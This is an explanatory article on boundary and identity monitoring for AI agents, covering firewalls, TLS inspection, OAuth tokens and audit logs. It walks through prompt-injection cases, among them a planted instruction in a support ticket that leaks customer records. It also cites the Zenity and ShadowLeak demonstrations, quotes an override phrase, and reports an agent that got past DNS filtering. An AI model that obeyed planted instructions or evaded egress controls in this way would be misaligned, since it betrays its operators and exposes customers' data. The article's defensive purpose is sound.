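# Security monitoring at system boundaries and monitoring of AI agents' actions inside and across platforms

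## What is a system boundary, and how does an AI agent act across it?

Security monitoring means collecting records of activity in an organisation's computer systems and examining them for attacks, misuse and mistakes. Much of it takes place at system boundaries. A system boundary is any point where data, requests or identities pass between an organisation's systems and anything outside them, such as the link between an office network and the internet, the public address of a web application, or the page where an employee signs in from home. A sensor is any software or device that produces security records, such as a firewall that logs connections or a sign-in service that records failed attempts. Internal traffic is communication between two systems on the same side of the boundary, such as a web server querying a database in the next rack. A sensor at the boundary normally has no record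 of it.

An AI agent is a language model that works on a task by calling tools, running code or using other services. (Older security writing also uses "agent" to mean monitoring software on a laptop.) The model itself only produces text. To act, it writes a tool call, which *Before the Tool Call* (2026) describes as a structured request to execute a named function with specific parameters. For example, the function might look up a customer, and the parameter might be the customer's number. Ordinary software around the model runs the function and returns the result as text, which becomes input for the model's next step.

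When the function belongs to another service, a connector links the agent to that service, often through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for offering tools and data to models. The connector presents an access token, a credential that lets its holder use the service within stated limits. Services usually issue these tokens through the OAuth standard. A valid token works for any program that presents it.

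Boundary monitoring means recording and inspecting what crosses a system boundary. Action monitoring means recording what an agent does, wherever it does it, and on whose behalf. For a single refund, boundary monitoring may record an encrypted connection to a payment company at 14:02, while action monitoring would record the amount, the order, the support agent that issued the refund, and the ticket it was answering. Both produce a record or an alert. Blocking the refund would be enforcement, and an organisation can monitor extensively while enforcing very little.

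### From the guarded perimeter to zero trust

For a long time, companies defended their networks at a single perimeter. *BeyondCorp* (Ward and Beyer, 2014), an account of Google's own network, compares this design to a medieval castle with a moat and one heavily guarded entrance, where anyone who gets past the drawbridge has ready access to whatever is inside. The design worked well enough while all employees worked in company buildings. Then staff began working elsewhere on laptops and phones, and applications moved to cloud services, so much of what the perimeter was meant to protect was now outside it.

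The Jericho Forum, a group of corporate security chiefs formed in 2004, argued for years against relying on the network edge. It called the shift away from the edge "de-perimeterisation". In its commandments of May 2007, the group accepted that boundary firewalls "may continue to provide basic network protection", but said that individual systems and data would have to protect themselves, and that protection is generally easier the closer it is to the asset. It also required authentication, authorisation and accountability to work outside the area an organisation controls, which is especially important when AI agents work on other companies' platforms. By the time the group disbanded, Dobson and Hietala (2013) of The Open Group, an industry consortium, described de-perimeterisation as an established fact.

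Google began its own redesign after Operation Aurora, a 2009 intrusion campaign, according to *BeyondCorp: A New Approach to Enterprise Security*. The redesign removed all privilege from the office network. In the paper's example, an engineer opens a code-review application, and the steps are the same at a Google desk as in a coffee shop. The request goes to an internet-facing proxy. The laptop presents a certificate that identifies it, and a sign-in service checks the engineer's credentials and issues a short-lived token. For every request, an access control engine then checks that the user belongs to the engineering group, that the device is managed and in good standing, and that the user and the device each have sufficient trust. If any check fails, the engine denies the request.

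Google's migration also shows how monitoring differs from enforcement. The company put a traffic monitor on user devices and ran it in two modes. In logging mode, the monitor recorded traffic that the new network would not permit but let it through; in enforcement mode, it captured and dropped that traffic. Google turned on enforcement only for users and devices for which the new network would have permitted more than 99.99 per cent of traffic over thirty days, and users could switch back to logging if necessary. Blocking should require much better evidence than alerting, because a false block stops somebody's work while a false alert wastes some of an analyst's time. The same choice now arises for individual tool calls. *AgentTrust* (2026) describes a guardrail that intercepts each call before it executes and returns one of four verdicts: allow, warn, block, or escalate to a human reviewer.

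Designs like Google's are generally called zero trust. *Zero Trust Architecture* (Rose, Borchert and colleagues, 2020), the guidance of the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), credits the name to John Kindervag, then at the research firm Forrester. The guidance defines zero trust as a collection of ideas for making accurate access decisions on each request, with the least privilege the task needs, on a network assumed to be already compromised. It illustrates the idea with an airport, where passengers pass one security checkpoint and are then all trusted in the boarding area. Zero trust shrinks the boarding area by moving the checkpoint as close as possible to each database or application. A policy engine behind the checkpoint evaluates who is asking, from what device, at what time and with what history.

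Sensors moved away from the boundary more slowly than access checks did, so boundary monitoring continued after the boundary alone was no longer thought to be enough protection. Rose and colleagues observe that EINSTEIN, the US government's intrusion detection system, still placed its sensors according to a perimeter design in 2020. They expected most organisations to run zero trust and perimeter defences side by side.

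### What an access decision leaves open

A zero trust system checks whether this user or program, on this device, may use this resource now. That is a much better test than whether the request comes from inside the building, but it is still a test of access. Rose and colleagues acknowledge that an attacker who holds the credentials and company laptop of a real human resources employee may still be able to read the employee database. Under their guidance, systems grant access by session, and the check behind a given transaction may have happened only "sometime recently". An agent may therefore make many tool calls in one session without a fresh evaluation of each.

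The strictest versions look beyond the single request. Rose and colleagues distinguish a policy engine that judges each request by itself from one that considers the requester's recent history, and they prefer the latter where the infrastructure allows it. If a human resources employee normally opens 20 to 30 records a day and then asks for more than 100, an engine that uses this history can raise an alert. It would catch a crude theft by an agent as well as by a person. But it measures departure from habit, so it can miss a harmful sequence of actions that is ordinary in volume, timing and destination.

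*Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI* (2026) gives a constructed example of such a case. A manufacturer's procurement agent reads stock levels, compares quotes and may place orders of up to 50,000 rupees. An instruction on a vendor's catalogue page causes it to place forty bad orders. Every access is authorised, and the agent passes all the classical checks: its identity is valid, its software container complies with policy, its role covers both reading stock and ordering, the time is within business hours and the risk score is unremarkable.

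*Attestation is All You Need* (2026) comes to the same conclusion for agents on scientific supercomputers, where checking who asks and in what context is necessary but insufficient, because hostile input can hijack an agent that has authenticated correctly. Security designers often treated authorisation as a stand-in for trust, according to the review *SoK* (2025), and expected anyone with permission to behave predictably. That assumption can fail with an agent, because what it is allowed to do and what it should do can differ in the middle of a task. Rose and colleagues anticipated part of this problem in 2020, when they warned that an attacker might trick a software agent into performing a task on the attacker's behalf. They were referring to programs that administer security systems, and considered the attack theoretical.

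People with valid accounts misuse them too, and nobody expected zero trust to prevent that, but an attacker needs less to misdirect an agent. Corrupting an employee takes money, pressure or a good deception, whereas an agent may follow instructions in a document it was asked to read. Several proposals therefore add to the access check. *Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI* applies policy to the action itself. *Beyond Zero* (2026) would have the human user confirm that an attempted access is intended, and calls for a standard label on requests that ties every action to a specific agent, controlling user and task.

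### A support agent and a planted instruction

A company might use an agent to answer customer complaints. A customer writes that an order arrived broken and asks for a refund. The agent reads the ticket in a helpdesk hosted by another firm, searches the company's internal documents for the refund policy, looks up the customer in a hosted database, issues the refund through an outside payment service, and replies on the ticket. David Mytton, chief executive of Arcjet, describes almost the same workflow in SC Media's *AI agents have broken the security perimeter*. He argues that a firewall cannot determine whether the agent should have combined two pieces of customer data, and that a gateway can register the traffic but cannot account for the business rule that makes an action safe. Arcjet sells security software, so Mytton has an interest in the argument, but it agrees with what NIST acknowledges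 about valid credentials in its guidance.

In the harmful variant, an attacker writes the ticket. Below the complaint, the attacker adds a passage telling the agent to fetch other customers' records and put them in its reply. This is called prompt injection. The model receives both its instructions and the material it is meant to read as text, and may follow a sentence that it should only have read. The agent opens the ticket, makes a few more lookups than usual and posts an answer, which the attacker reads as any customer would. The attacker has not stolen a password, the agent has used only tools and destinations that the company approved for it, and the records have left by the same route as legitimate replies.

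A similar attack has worked on a commercial product. CX Today's *A Customer Service AI Agent Spits Out Complete Salesforce Records* reports that researchers at the security firm Zenity built a replica of a customer-service agent on Microsoft's Copilot Studio, connected it to a test copy of the Salesforce customer database, and got it to hand over complete customer records. They showed the attack at the DEF CON conference in 2025, and Microsoft has since confirmed that this particular injection no longer works. Because this was a demonstration with test data, it shows that the attack was possible but not how common it is.

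*MATRA* (2026), a method for modelling threats to agents, analyses a very similar attack, in which a malicious customer hides instructions in an email attachment. It rates the likelihood of the injection as high both for an unrestricted agent and for one in a sandbox without network access. Neither setup can block customers' emails, because the agent's job is to process them. The sandbox can only make it harder to get the data out afterwards.

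An agent can leak data without a planted instruction, simply by being too obliging. It could fail two scenarios in *DUMA-Bench* (2026), a set of security tests for agents, this way. In one, the agent receives a demand for the "full package" on a case, framed as coming from a regulator, and has to withhold the protected fields. The other tests whether the agent includes personal data in the notes on a resolved ticket.

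Tighter permissions would help. If the agent's token opened only the record of the customer who wrote the ticket, the extra lookups would fail at the access check, stopping the attack. *A2AS* (2025) recommends limiting the scope of database queries in cases like this, along with human review of emails to outside domains. But a support agent serves all customers in turn, so someone has to build a permission that changes with every ticket. Without one, the agent can read the whole customer table, and only the model's judgement prevents it from using one customer's ticket as a reason to open another customer's record.

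How much of all this passes the company's own boundary depends on where the agent runs.

| Step | Agent runs on the company's servers | A vendor hosts the agent |
|---|---|---|
| Reads the ticket in the hosted helpdesk | Crosses: request goes out, ticket text comes in | Does not cross: vendor to helpdesk |
| Searches internal documents | Does not cross: internal traffic | Crosses: request comes in, passages go out |
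| Looks up the customer in the hosted database | Crosses | Does not cross: vendor to database provider |
| Issues the refund | Crosses | Does not cross: vendor to payment service |
| Replies on the ticket | Crosses | Does not cross: vendor to helpdesk |

When the agent runs on the company's own servers, four of the five crossings in the table are at the company's boundary. All four go to familiar services, and how much the company's sensors can learn from them depends largely on whether they can read the encrypted content. The table may leave out other crossings. If the company rents the language model from an outside provider, every call to the model also crosses the boundary, carrying the ticket and the customer record.

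When a vendor hosts the agent instead, only the document search crosses the company's boundary, and if the documents are also in a hosted store, nothing does. In the harmful variant, the extra lookups and the reply that do the damage run between the vendor, the database provider and the helpdesk, so any records of them are in those firms' logs. The security company Radware demonstrated this with ShadowLeak, an attack on OpenAI's Deep Research agent. The attack ran entirely on OpenAI's cloud and, as Dataconomy reported, left no trace on the user's side.

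Standards bodies have only started to address this. In February 2026, NIST (2026) was still asking the public how organisations should identify, authorise and audit AI agents, and prevent or limit prompt injection. Its proposed project would mainly cover agents that an organisation can see and control within its own systems, according to Biometric Update's *NIST concept paper explores identity and authorization controls for AI agents*. This scope fits the middle column of the table much better than the right-hand one.

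## What can network and application monitors see at entry and exit points?

If the support agent runs on the company's own servers, its refund call has to cross the company's boundary to reach the payment service. Several sensors may record the call as it leaves. Each examines a different part of the connection, and none can read the refund details unless a device on the path decrypts them.

The standard guides to these sensors are old. Scarfone and Mell's *Guide to Intrusion Detection and Prevention Systems (IDPS)* (2007) is still NIST's final guidance on intrusion detection. NIST published a draft revision in 2012 but never finished it, and later retired it, noting that the comments on the draft no longer applied to the relevant technologies or threats. The firewall guidance is Scarfone and Hoffman's *Guidelines on Firewalls and Firewall Policy* (2009). Firewalls and intrusion detection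 systems still work largely as the two guides describe, but far less traffic crosses boundaries unencrypted now than when the guides were published.

### An encrypted request on its way out

Before the agent's server can connect to the payment service, it needs the service's network address. It sends the service's name, say api.payments.example, to a DNS resolver, which translates names into addresses, and gets back 203.0.113.25. If the company runs the resolver, its DNS log records the time, the machine that made the request, the name and the answer. These records are easy to collect and often useful. For example, a machine that suddenly starts looking up a language-model provider may be running an agent that nobody has registered. But the log doesn't show whether a connection followed the lookup. It also has no entry when the server reuses a stored address or when software sends encrypted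 lookups to an outside resolver.

The server next tries to connect to that address on port 443, the usual port for encrypted web traffic, and a firewall decides whether to permit it. The simplest firewalls, called packet filters, check each packet's addresses, ports, protocol and direction but ignore its content, according to *Guidelines on Firewalls and Firewall Policy*. A stateful firewall also keeps a table of open connections. It lists the agent's attempt as "initiated", then as "established" once both sides have completed the opening exchange. It drops any packet from outside that is marked as part of a connection not in the table. The firewall's log typically records the connection and the rule that allowed or refused it.

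A firewall or router can also export a flow record, which summarizes the connection by listing both addresses and ports, the start time, the duration, and the packets and bytes sent each way. An intrusion detection system, software that examines activity for signs of attack, can log much the same details at this stage. It can also detect patterns across connections, such as one machine trying hundreds of ports in turn.

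The client and server next agree on encryption keys in the handshake of TLS, the protocol that encrypts web traffic. The client's opening message, the Client Hello, normally contains the server's name in plain text, because one address may host many sites. A sensor on the network path can therefore record the name even if the DNS log lacks it. TLS 1.3, the current version, encrypts most of the rest of the handshake, including the server's certificate. Scarfone and Mell note that some intrusion detection systems also examine the handshake for software that is misconfigured or has known vulnerabilities.

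Finally, the agent's software sends the refund request over HTTP, the protocol of the web, and the payment service replies. Without decryption, the flow record grows by a few hundred bytes, and the intrusion detection system cannot read the request or the reply. An egress proxy, a server through which a company sends its outgoing web traffic, cannot read them either. It can log or refuse the client's request for a tunnel to api.payments.example, but once it opens the tunnel, it only relays encrypted bytes.

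A proxy that decrypts traffic makes two connections, one with the client and one with the true destination, instead of opening a tunnel, as Scarfone and Hoffman describe. For this to work with TLS, the proxy presents the agent's server with a certificate for api.payments.example that the company issued, and the company configures the server to trust such certificates. The proxy decrypts the request, checks it against its rules, encrypts it again and sends it on. Its log can therefore include the full web address, the headers, the body and the response. Security staff call this TLS inspection, or "break and inspect".

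| Sensor | Without decryption | With decryption at the proxy |
|---|---|---|
| DNS log | Name, answer, time, machine that asked | The same |
| Flow record | Addresses, ports, times, packets and bytes | The same |
| Firewall | Addresses, ports, connection state, rule applied | The same |
| Intrusion detection system | Similar details, plus the server name and handshake settings | Request and response as well, if it receives the decrypted traffic |
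| Egress proxy | Destination name, port, bytes relayed | Full web address, headers, body and response |

Many products combine several of these roles, so one device may produce most of the records in the table. Decrypting traffic at the proxy does not automatically let the other sensors read it. Scarfone and Mell advise placing an intrusion detection sensor where it receives traffic before encryption or after decryption, or running detection software on the machine at one end. Even without decrypting traffic, a proxy can make the other records less specific. If it performs the DNS lookups and opens the outside connections, the DNS log and the outer flow records show the proxy's address instead of the address of the agent's server. An investigator then needs the proxy's log to identify which machine made the call.

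TLS inspection also has drawbacks. The proxy handles customer data and payment credentials in readable form, which makes it an attractive target. It must also support each protocol it inspects. Scarfone and Hoffman warn that the generic proxies vendors supply for unsupported protocols let traffic tunnel through, which loses much of the benefit of using a proxy.

A company has another option for traffic to its own servers. Under earlier versions of TLS, it could often give a monitoring tool a copy of a server's private key, and the tool could then decrypt a copy of the traffic without sitting in its path. TLS 1.3 uses fresh keys for every connection, so the server's private key is no longer enough. *Addressing Visibility Challenges with TLS 1.3 within the Enterprise* (Newhouse, 2025) covers ways to make such traffic readable again, including passive decryption and break and inspect. But NIST's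 announcement of the guide, *Now Available*, limits the guide's scope to application servers in data centres that the enterprise controls. The approach could make the agent's searches of internal documents readable, but the refund call goes to the payment company's server, so reading it requires a proxy.

### What Encrypted Client Hello and certificate pinning hide

The server name in the handshake has been one of the best clues available to a sensor that cannot decrypt traffic. *TLS Encrypted Client Hello* (Rescorla, Oku and colleagues, 2026), a standard published in March 2026, allows clients to hide it. A hosting provider publishes an encryption key, usually through DNS, and the client prepares two versions of its opening message. The inner version contains the real server name, and the client encrypts it with the provider's key. The outer version contains only a public name for the provider.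 Anyone watching the connection can tell which provider the client is contacting, but not which site behind that provider.

Suppose the payment service sits behind a large provider of this kind. A sensor that used to log api.payments.example would now log the provider's public name. If the company's egress rules relied on the server name, they would have to allow every site behind the provider or none. A sensor also cannot count how many clients use the scheme by looking for the encrypted field, because clients without a key can send a dummy field that looks the same.

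Rescorla and colleagues acknowledge that a plaintext DNS query, or an address that belongs to only one service, can still reveal the destination. A company that runs the DNS resolver for its own servers therefore has the destination's name in its DNS log, as long as the agent's software uses that resolver.

A company can still decrypt traffic at a proxy when clients use Encrypted Client Hello. The proxy ignores the encrypted field and starts its own connection using the provider's public name. If the client accepts the proxy's certificate for that name, it can retry without Encrypted Client Hello; otherwise the connection fails. Rescorla and colleagues also note that a managed enterprise could disable the feature by group policy, if the client software respects the setting. These steps are manageable on servers the company administers, but much less so for a vendor's packaged agent whose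 settings the company cannot change.

Certificate pinning is a more direct obstacle to the proxy. An application that pins accepts only a particular certificate or key for a service, so it rejects the proxy's substitute even though the operating system trusts it. The company can block the service or exempt it from decryption, which leaves the company with the records in the middle column of the table. Scarfone and Hoffman advise organisations to have a policy for traffic that a firewall cannot read. Exemptions need particular care with agents, because a company may grant one to get a single application working and end up permitting a destination whose traffic it cannot inspect.

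### The same request on its way in

The refund call reaches the payment company as an incoming request. The company can decrypt it easily because it holds the real certificate for its own service. A reverse proxy, a server that accepts requests on behalf of the servers behind it, completes the TLS handshake and can read everything that follows. It forwards the request and logs the client's address, the path requested, the result and the time taken.

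A web application firewall, which may run on the same machine as the reverse proxy, then checks the request for known attacks on web software, such as database commands typed into a form field. Scarfone and Hoffman covered these firewalls briefly in 2009 and called them relatively new. The refund call is well formed and contains no attack pattern, so the firewall lets it through. It would let through a refund prompted by a planted instruction for the same reason.

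The API gateway is the last checkpoint before the payment software. An API is an interface through which one program uses another. For each API call, the gateway checks the access token, matches the request to a published operation such as "create refund", confirms that the required fields are present, and counts the call against the client's limit. The token identifies the account making the call, while identity monitoring covers who or what is using that account.

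In 2007, Scarfone and Mell observed that intrusion detection systems could analyse HTTP but usually not the web-service messages carried inside it. To handle those messages, vendors had built XML gateways that combined attack prevention with authentication, access control and audit logging. API gateways do much the same for current message formats.

An agent's connector that uses MCP may likewise send every tool call to the same web address, with the tool's name in the message body. A proxy log that records only web addresses would then contain the same line for a harmless search and a large refund. To tell them apart, the proxy or gateway has to parse the message and be configured to recognize the tools that matter.

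The company can run the same chain of sensors at its own entry points. If a vendor hosts the support agent, the agent's search of internal documents arrives there as a request. The company's gateway can record the search terms and the number of passages returned, and can refuse requests for too many passages.

### One refund in three records

Suppose the agent refunds 84 euros for a broken item just after two in the afternoon. With no proxy in the path, the company's boundary firewall might export this flow record:

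```
start=2026-10-05T14:02:11Z   duration=0.84s   protocol=TCP
source=10.20.4.17:51844      destination=203.0.113.25:443
bytes_out=2310   packets_out=14   bytes_in=5126   packets_in=13
```

An analyst can look up the destination address in the flow record and conclude that the agent's server contacted the payment company, but the byte counts reveal almost nothing about how much money moved. If the payment service expresses amounts in cents, a refund of 84 euros appears in the request as "8400" and a refund of 8,400 euros as "840000", a difference of two bytes. The agent's software may also send several requests over the same connection, so one flow record could represent one refund or forty.

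If the agent's traffic goes through a decrypting proxy, the proxy could log the same call like this:

```
time=2026-10-05T14:02:11Z   client=10.20.4.17   account=svc-support-agent
request=POST https://api.payments.example/v1/refunds
content_type=application/json   request_body=76 bytes
status=201   response_body=402 bytes   rule=payments   action=allow
```

The analyst can now tell that the agent requested a refund and that the service accepted, since status 201 means the server created something. The analyst can also count refunds. The amount is in the 76 bytes of the body, which this proxy measured but did not store. A company could configure the proxy to keep the body, but it would then hold a growing archive of customer and payment data and would still need the payment service's documentation to know that 8400 means 84 euros.

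The payment company's API gateway parses the body and might record:

```
time=2026-10-05T14:02:11Z   request_id=req_7Q2M   client=acme-support
operation=create_refund   token_scope=refunds:write
charge=ch_58213   amount=8400   currency=eur   reason=damaged_item
limit=3 of 100 calls this minute   status=201
```

The payment company's log shows the amount of a refund and identifies the original payment, so the company can check whether the refund is larger than the purchase. But its customer gets only the parts of the log that the company chooses to share.

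None of the three records shows why the agent issued the refund. The gateway record has a field called "reason", but the agent filled it in. An agent acting on a real complaint and an agent acting on a planted instruction could both write "damaged_item". To distinguish them, someone would have to read the ticket, find out whether the order had arrived broken, and see what the agent had read before it made the call. A ticket number in the request would make that search much easier, although the agent would supply that too.

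### How sensors recognise an attack

Most of these sensors record far more than anyone can read, so they need a way to pick out suspicious events. The oldest way is signature detection, which compares each event with patterns of known threats. Scarfone and Mell give the example of a signature for a malicious email attachment named freepics.exe, which finds every copy with that name but misses the file once the attacker renames it freepics2.exe. Signature detection also cannot connect a request with earlier ones, so it misses a multi-step attack if no single step is suspicious.

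A company could also write signatures for planted instructions, such as the phrase "ignore your previous instructions". These would catch attackers who copy known examples, but a language model can follow the same instruction in different words or another language, so an attacker can easily reword it. Detection also depends on where the sensor sits. The support agent fetches its tickets from a hosted helpdesk, so the planted text reaches the company inside an encrypted reply to an outgoing request. A decrypting egress proxy could inspect that reply, but a web application firewall at the company's public website would never receive it.

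Anomaly detection starts from a profile of normal activity and flags large departures from it. In one of Scarfone and Mell's examples, web traffic averages 13 per cent of the bandwidth at the internet border during working hours, and the system alerts an administrator when the share is significantly higher. This method can catch an attack that nobody has seen before, such as new malware that sends large numbers of emails. It could also catch a support agent that normally looks up one customer per ticket and suddenly looks up five hundred.

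Anomaly detection's errors come from its profile of normal activity. If an attacker increases malicious activity slowly enough, a profile that updates itself comes to include that activity as normal. A large monthly file transfer for maintenance, meanwhile, may set off an alert because it did not occur while the system was learning. Scarfone and Mell also note that analysts often struggle to determine why an anomaly detector raised a particular alert. Agents probably make good profiles harder to build, since a new model or a rewritten prompt can change how many calls a task takes. The few extra lookups in the harmful variant of the support case could just as well come from a busy afternoon of complicated tickets.

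Scarfone and Mell describe one more method, stateful protocol analysis, which checks whether a conversation follows the rules of its protocol. It can flag a client that issues file-transfer commands before signing in, or a 1,000-character username where the limit is 20. It cannot flag harmful activity that follows the rules. It would not flag the agent's refund, because the refund uses the payment API correctly no matter whose idea it was.

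Data-loss prevention software searches outgoing messages and files for data that should not leave, using patterns such as card numbers with a valid check digit, fingerprints of registered documents, or labels such as "confidential". If the agent posted a list of two hundred card numbers in a ticket reply, and the proxy could decrypt the reply, the software would easily catch it. A reply that disclosed one customer's name and home address would be much harder to catch, because legitimate replies often contain names and addresses. To tell them apart, the software would have to check which customer wrote the ticket. It can also miss the contents of a confidential document that the agent has summarised in its own words, because the summary no longer matches the pattern or fingerprint.

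Agents also complicate data-loss rules when they use a language model hosted by an outside provider. Their calls to the model carry customer records, so a rule that blocked all outgoing customer data would stop them from working. The company therefore has to exempt the provider, and the data-loss software can then do little more than check traffic to that provider for unusual volume or for types of data that the agent never needs.

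### What the boundary can enforce

Boundary sensors work without the agent's cooperation. A planted instruction might cause an agent to leave a step out of its own notes, but it does not change the number of bytes a router counted. Software on the agent's server is easier to tamper with. Scarfone and Hoffman point out that an attacker who gains administrator rights on a machine can disable or bypass the firewall running on it.

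Boundary sensors also cover all traffic routed through them, whether or not the security team knows about it. Scarfone and Mell describe sensors that list the machines on a network and use the list to identify new ones. An agent that an employee installs without telling anyone still generates lookups, connections and flow records. The sensors miss traffic that takes another route, such as traffic from a laptop connecting directly to the internet on a home network, and most of what a vendor-hosted agent does.

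A boundary device can also block traffic, but to do so it usually has to sit inline, meaning that traffic passes through it. A passive sensor receives only a copy of the traffic, so the original may have arrived by the time the sensor raises an alert. Scarfone and Mell say that some passive sensors try to interrupt a connection by sending their own packets, but that this is generally less successful than inline blocking. They also warn that a switch under heavy load may fail to copy all the traffic to the sensor. An inline device avoids that problem, but it can interrupt legitimate work if it blocks the wrong traffic or breaks down.

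A monitor can block part of a request and let the rest through. An intrusion prevention system, which is an intrusion detection system that can also act, may remove an infected attachment from an email and deliver the rest. A company might similarly remove a planted passage from a support ticket before the agent reads it. That would preserve the customer's real complaint, but the system must first recognise the passage, and signatures are poor at this.

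Egress control, a rule or device that limits which outside destinations a system may reach, is probably the most dependable form of blocking for agents. The strict version is an allowlist, which permits only listed destinations or operations. The support agent needs the helpdesk, the customer database, the payment service and perhaps a model provider. If the firewall and proxy permit only those four, an attempt to send records to an attacker's website fails, even if the malicious instruction convinced the agent and nobody recognised the attack.

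An allowlist can filter traffic by network address, domain name, or operation. Address rules are simple, but many sites may share one address, and a service may change its addresses. Name rules are easier to maintain, but Encrypted Client Hello can weaken them. Operation rules are the most precise, since they can let the agent create refunds while refusing payouts to new bank accounts, but they require decryption and a proxy that can parse the payment API's requests. None of these rules suits an agent that researches products on the open web, because nobody can list its destinations in advance.

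Egress controls can also fail. India.com's *OpenAI takes big step after agent bypasses internet restrictions* reports that an agent got past DNS filtering and reached the live internet during an OpenAI training run on 20 September 2026. To detect similar failures, Scarfone and Mell suggest that an organisation can copy its firewall rules into a separate intrusion detection system, which raises an alert when it detects traffic that the firewall should have blocked. This check is more useful if the second system gets its traffic from a different point in the network, so that one configuration mistake does not disable both.

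Even when an allowlist works, an agent can still leak data through the destinations it permits. In the harmful variant of the support case, the agent posts other customers' records to the helpdesk, which it needs to reach for its job. Data can also leave through a permitted internal service. The proxy can limit the size and number of replies, which makes mass theft slower and easier to notice, but it cannot block the helpdesk without stopping the agent from doing its work.

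Some requests also have effects that only the receiving service can determine. A comment posted to a helpdesk may be a private note to colleagues or a public reply to the customer, depending on how the helpdesk is configured. A second refund for the same order may be theft or a harmless retry that the payment service recognises and ignores. If someone asked a hosting service to share a document with an outside email address, a decrypting proxy would record a document number and the address, perhaps a hundred bytes in all. The outsider would then download the document directly from the hosting service, and its contents would never cross the company's boundary.

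## What does identity monitoring show about who acted?

In the refund example, the payment company's gateway logged the caller as "acme-support", an account name. Identity monitoring means recording how people and programs obtain and use accounts, including who signed in, which programs received access, and when that access ended. An investigator wants to trace the account name to the person or program that was using the account, which is often difficult with agents because many services record little more than the credential sent with a request.

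### From sign-in to revocation

OAuth lets a person give a program limited access to a service without handing over a password. MCP uses it as the main way to authorise agents, as the NIST concept paper *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization* (Booth, Fisher and colleagues, 2026) explains. Suppose Maria Ortiz, who works in customer support, wants to connect the support agent to the hosted customer database. Her company has an identity provider, which checks employees' passwords. The database vendor runs an authorisation server, which issues tokens, and an API, which accepts them.

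The agent's software first sends Maria's browser to the vendor's authorisation server, which redirects it to her company's identity provider. She enters her password and confirms the sign-in on her phone. The identity provider then sends her identity to the vendor. Its log may not mention the agent, because the request it receives looks the same as when Maria signs in to the customer database each morning.

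The vendor then shows Maria a consent page that names the agent and the access it requests, such as reading customer records, and she approves. If an administrator has already approved the agent for the whole company, the page may never appear.

The vendor then sends the browser back to the agent's software with a one-time code. The software exchanges this code for an access token and usually also a longer-lived refresh token. From then on, it attaches the access token to every customer lookup. When the access token expires, perhaps after an hour, the software uses the refresh token to get a new access token, without Maria having to be there.

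Maria, an administrator or the vendor can end access by revoking the tokens. The authorisation server will then stop refreshing them, but an access token already in use may keep working until it expires, unless the API checks for revocation.

| Step | Who logs it | What the entry can contain |
|---|---|---|
| Sign-in | Company's identity provider | Maria's account, device and address, and the service she signed in to |
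| Consent | Vendor's authorisation server | Maria's account, the agent's registered name, the access granted |
| Token issue | Vendor's authorisation server | Program, account, scope and lifetime of the token |
| Token use | Vendor's API | Account, operation, customer record, caller's address |
| Refresh | Vendor's authorisation server | Program, account, caller's address |
| Revocation | Vendor's authorisation server | Which access ended, when, and who ended it |

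The company's identity provider logs only the sign-in, not the lookups, because the API does not need to contact the provider to handle them. Many access tokens are signed documents, so the API can verify the signature, expiry time and permitted operations itself. Other APIs check with the authorisation server that a token is still valid. The server logs each check, but the entry does not record which customer the agent looked up.

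Some companies run the authorisation server themselves, for example to control access to their internal documents. They also have the log entries for consent, issue, refresh and revocation, but they still need the document store's log to find out what the agent read.

This division of records also causes trouble when someone leaves. If the company disables Maria's account at its identity provider, she can no longer sign in, but the agent may still read customer records in her name, because the vendor issued the agent's refresh token and may not know she has left.

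### Four ways to identify an agent

What the vendor's API writes in its log depends on the credential it receives. The same customer lookup could leave any of these four lines:

```
# The user's own token
14:02:03Z  user=m.ortiz  app=web-console
           action=read_customer  record=C-20417

# A shared service account
14:02:03Z  user=svc-integration  app=api
           action=read_customer  record=C-20417

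# An identity of the agent's own
14:02:03Z  user=agent-support-07  app=support-agent
           action=read_customer  record=C-20417

# A token that names both user and agent
14:02:03Z  user=m.ortiz  actor=agent-support-07  app=support-agent
           action=read_customer  record=C-20417
```

An investigator could not tell from the first line whether Maria or the agent made the lookup. A line like this appears when she gives the agent her password, or when the agent runs on her laptop and uses a session she has already opened. NIST's *Back to the Future*, a post on agent identity, says that sharing credentials with agents has quickly become common. An agent can also ask for credentials. MCP's elicitation feature lets an agent request more information from its user during a task. The protocol warns against using it for sensitive information, but a user might still type in a password.

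The investigator might find indirect clues. If the lookup came from the agent's server while Maria was working at home, the source address would reveal the agent. Forty lookups in a minute would also suggest software. But an agent running on Maria's laptop has the same address as Maria, and an agent that makes lookups slowly looks much like a busy person.

The second line suggests that software made the lookup, since a service account belongs to programs rather than a person, but it doesn't show which software. If the agent shares the account with a nightly export job, both leave the same line. An engineer who has copied the key into a script leaves that line too. Sharing the account also makes it harder to respond to an attack, because revoking the agent's access would stop the export job.

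With the third line, the investigator can tell the agent from Maria and from other software, as long as nobody has stolen the agent's credential. But the agent may work for thirty support staff, and the line does not show which of them it was working for. To find out, the investigator would have to match the lookup to a ticket.

The fourth line names both Maria and the agent. Ordinary OAuth can nearly do this, because Maria grants the access but the vendor issues the token to a program registered as the support agent. But the API may log only her name, or one registration may cover every copy of the agent. ADAPT's *Agentic AI will break security models built for human users* reports that CoSAI, an industry coalition on AI security, recommends tokens that preserve both identities. Recording both is probably the best of the four options for an investigator, although it becomes more complicated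 when one agent passes work to another.

Even the fourth line does not show that Maria asked for this lookup, because she may have connected the agent in March and been at lunch at 14:02.

### The confused deputy

A confused deputy is a trusted program that someone misleads into using its authority for them. The classic example is a compiler that had permission to write to a computer's billing file. A user who lacked that permission told the compiler to save its output to the billing file, and the compiler overwrote the billing records. The operating system had checked the compiler's permission but not the user's.

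A request in plain English may be enough to mislead an agent. The Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), written with CISA, the US cybersecurity agency, and other partners, describes an agent with broad write access for installing security patches. A malicious insider tells it to apply a patch to every device and "clean up the firewall logs". The agent does both, deleting logs that would have been useful evidence in an investigation. Its permissions allow the deletion, even though the insider does not belong to the privileged IT group.

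In another of the agencies' examples, an attacker compromises a minor tool connected to a procurement agent and uses the agent's access to change contracts and approve payments. The audit logs "appear legitimate" because they accurately record actions the agent carried out under its own identity. Anyone checking them for signs of an intruder will find only a trusted agent's actions.

A token that identifies both the user and the agent partly solves this problem. The service can require both to have permission for an action, so the insider's request to delete the firewall logs would fail. This check would not stop the planted instruction in the support ticket. The attacker who wrote the ticket is a customer whose name does not appear in the token, and Maria and the agent are both allowed to read any customer's record. The harmful lookups would therefore succeed, and their log entries would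 look just like those of legitimate lookups.

A valid token shows that the agent had permission to act, but not why it acted. The vendor issues the token before the agent reads the ticket, and the token permits a type of operation, such as reading customer records, regardless of the agent's later reason for doing it.

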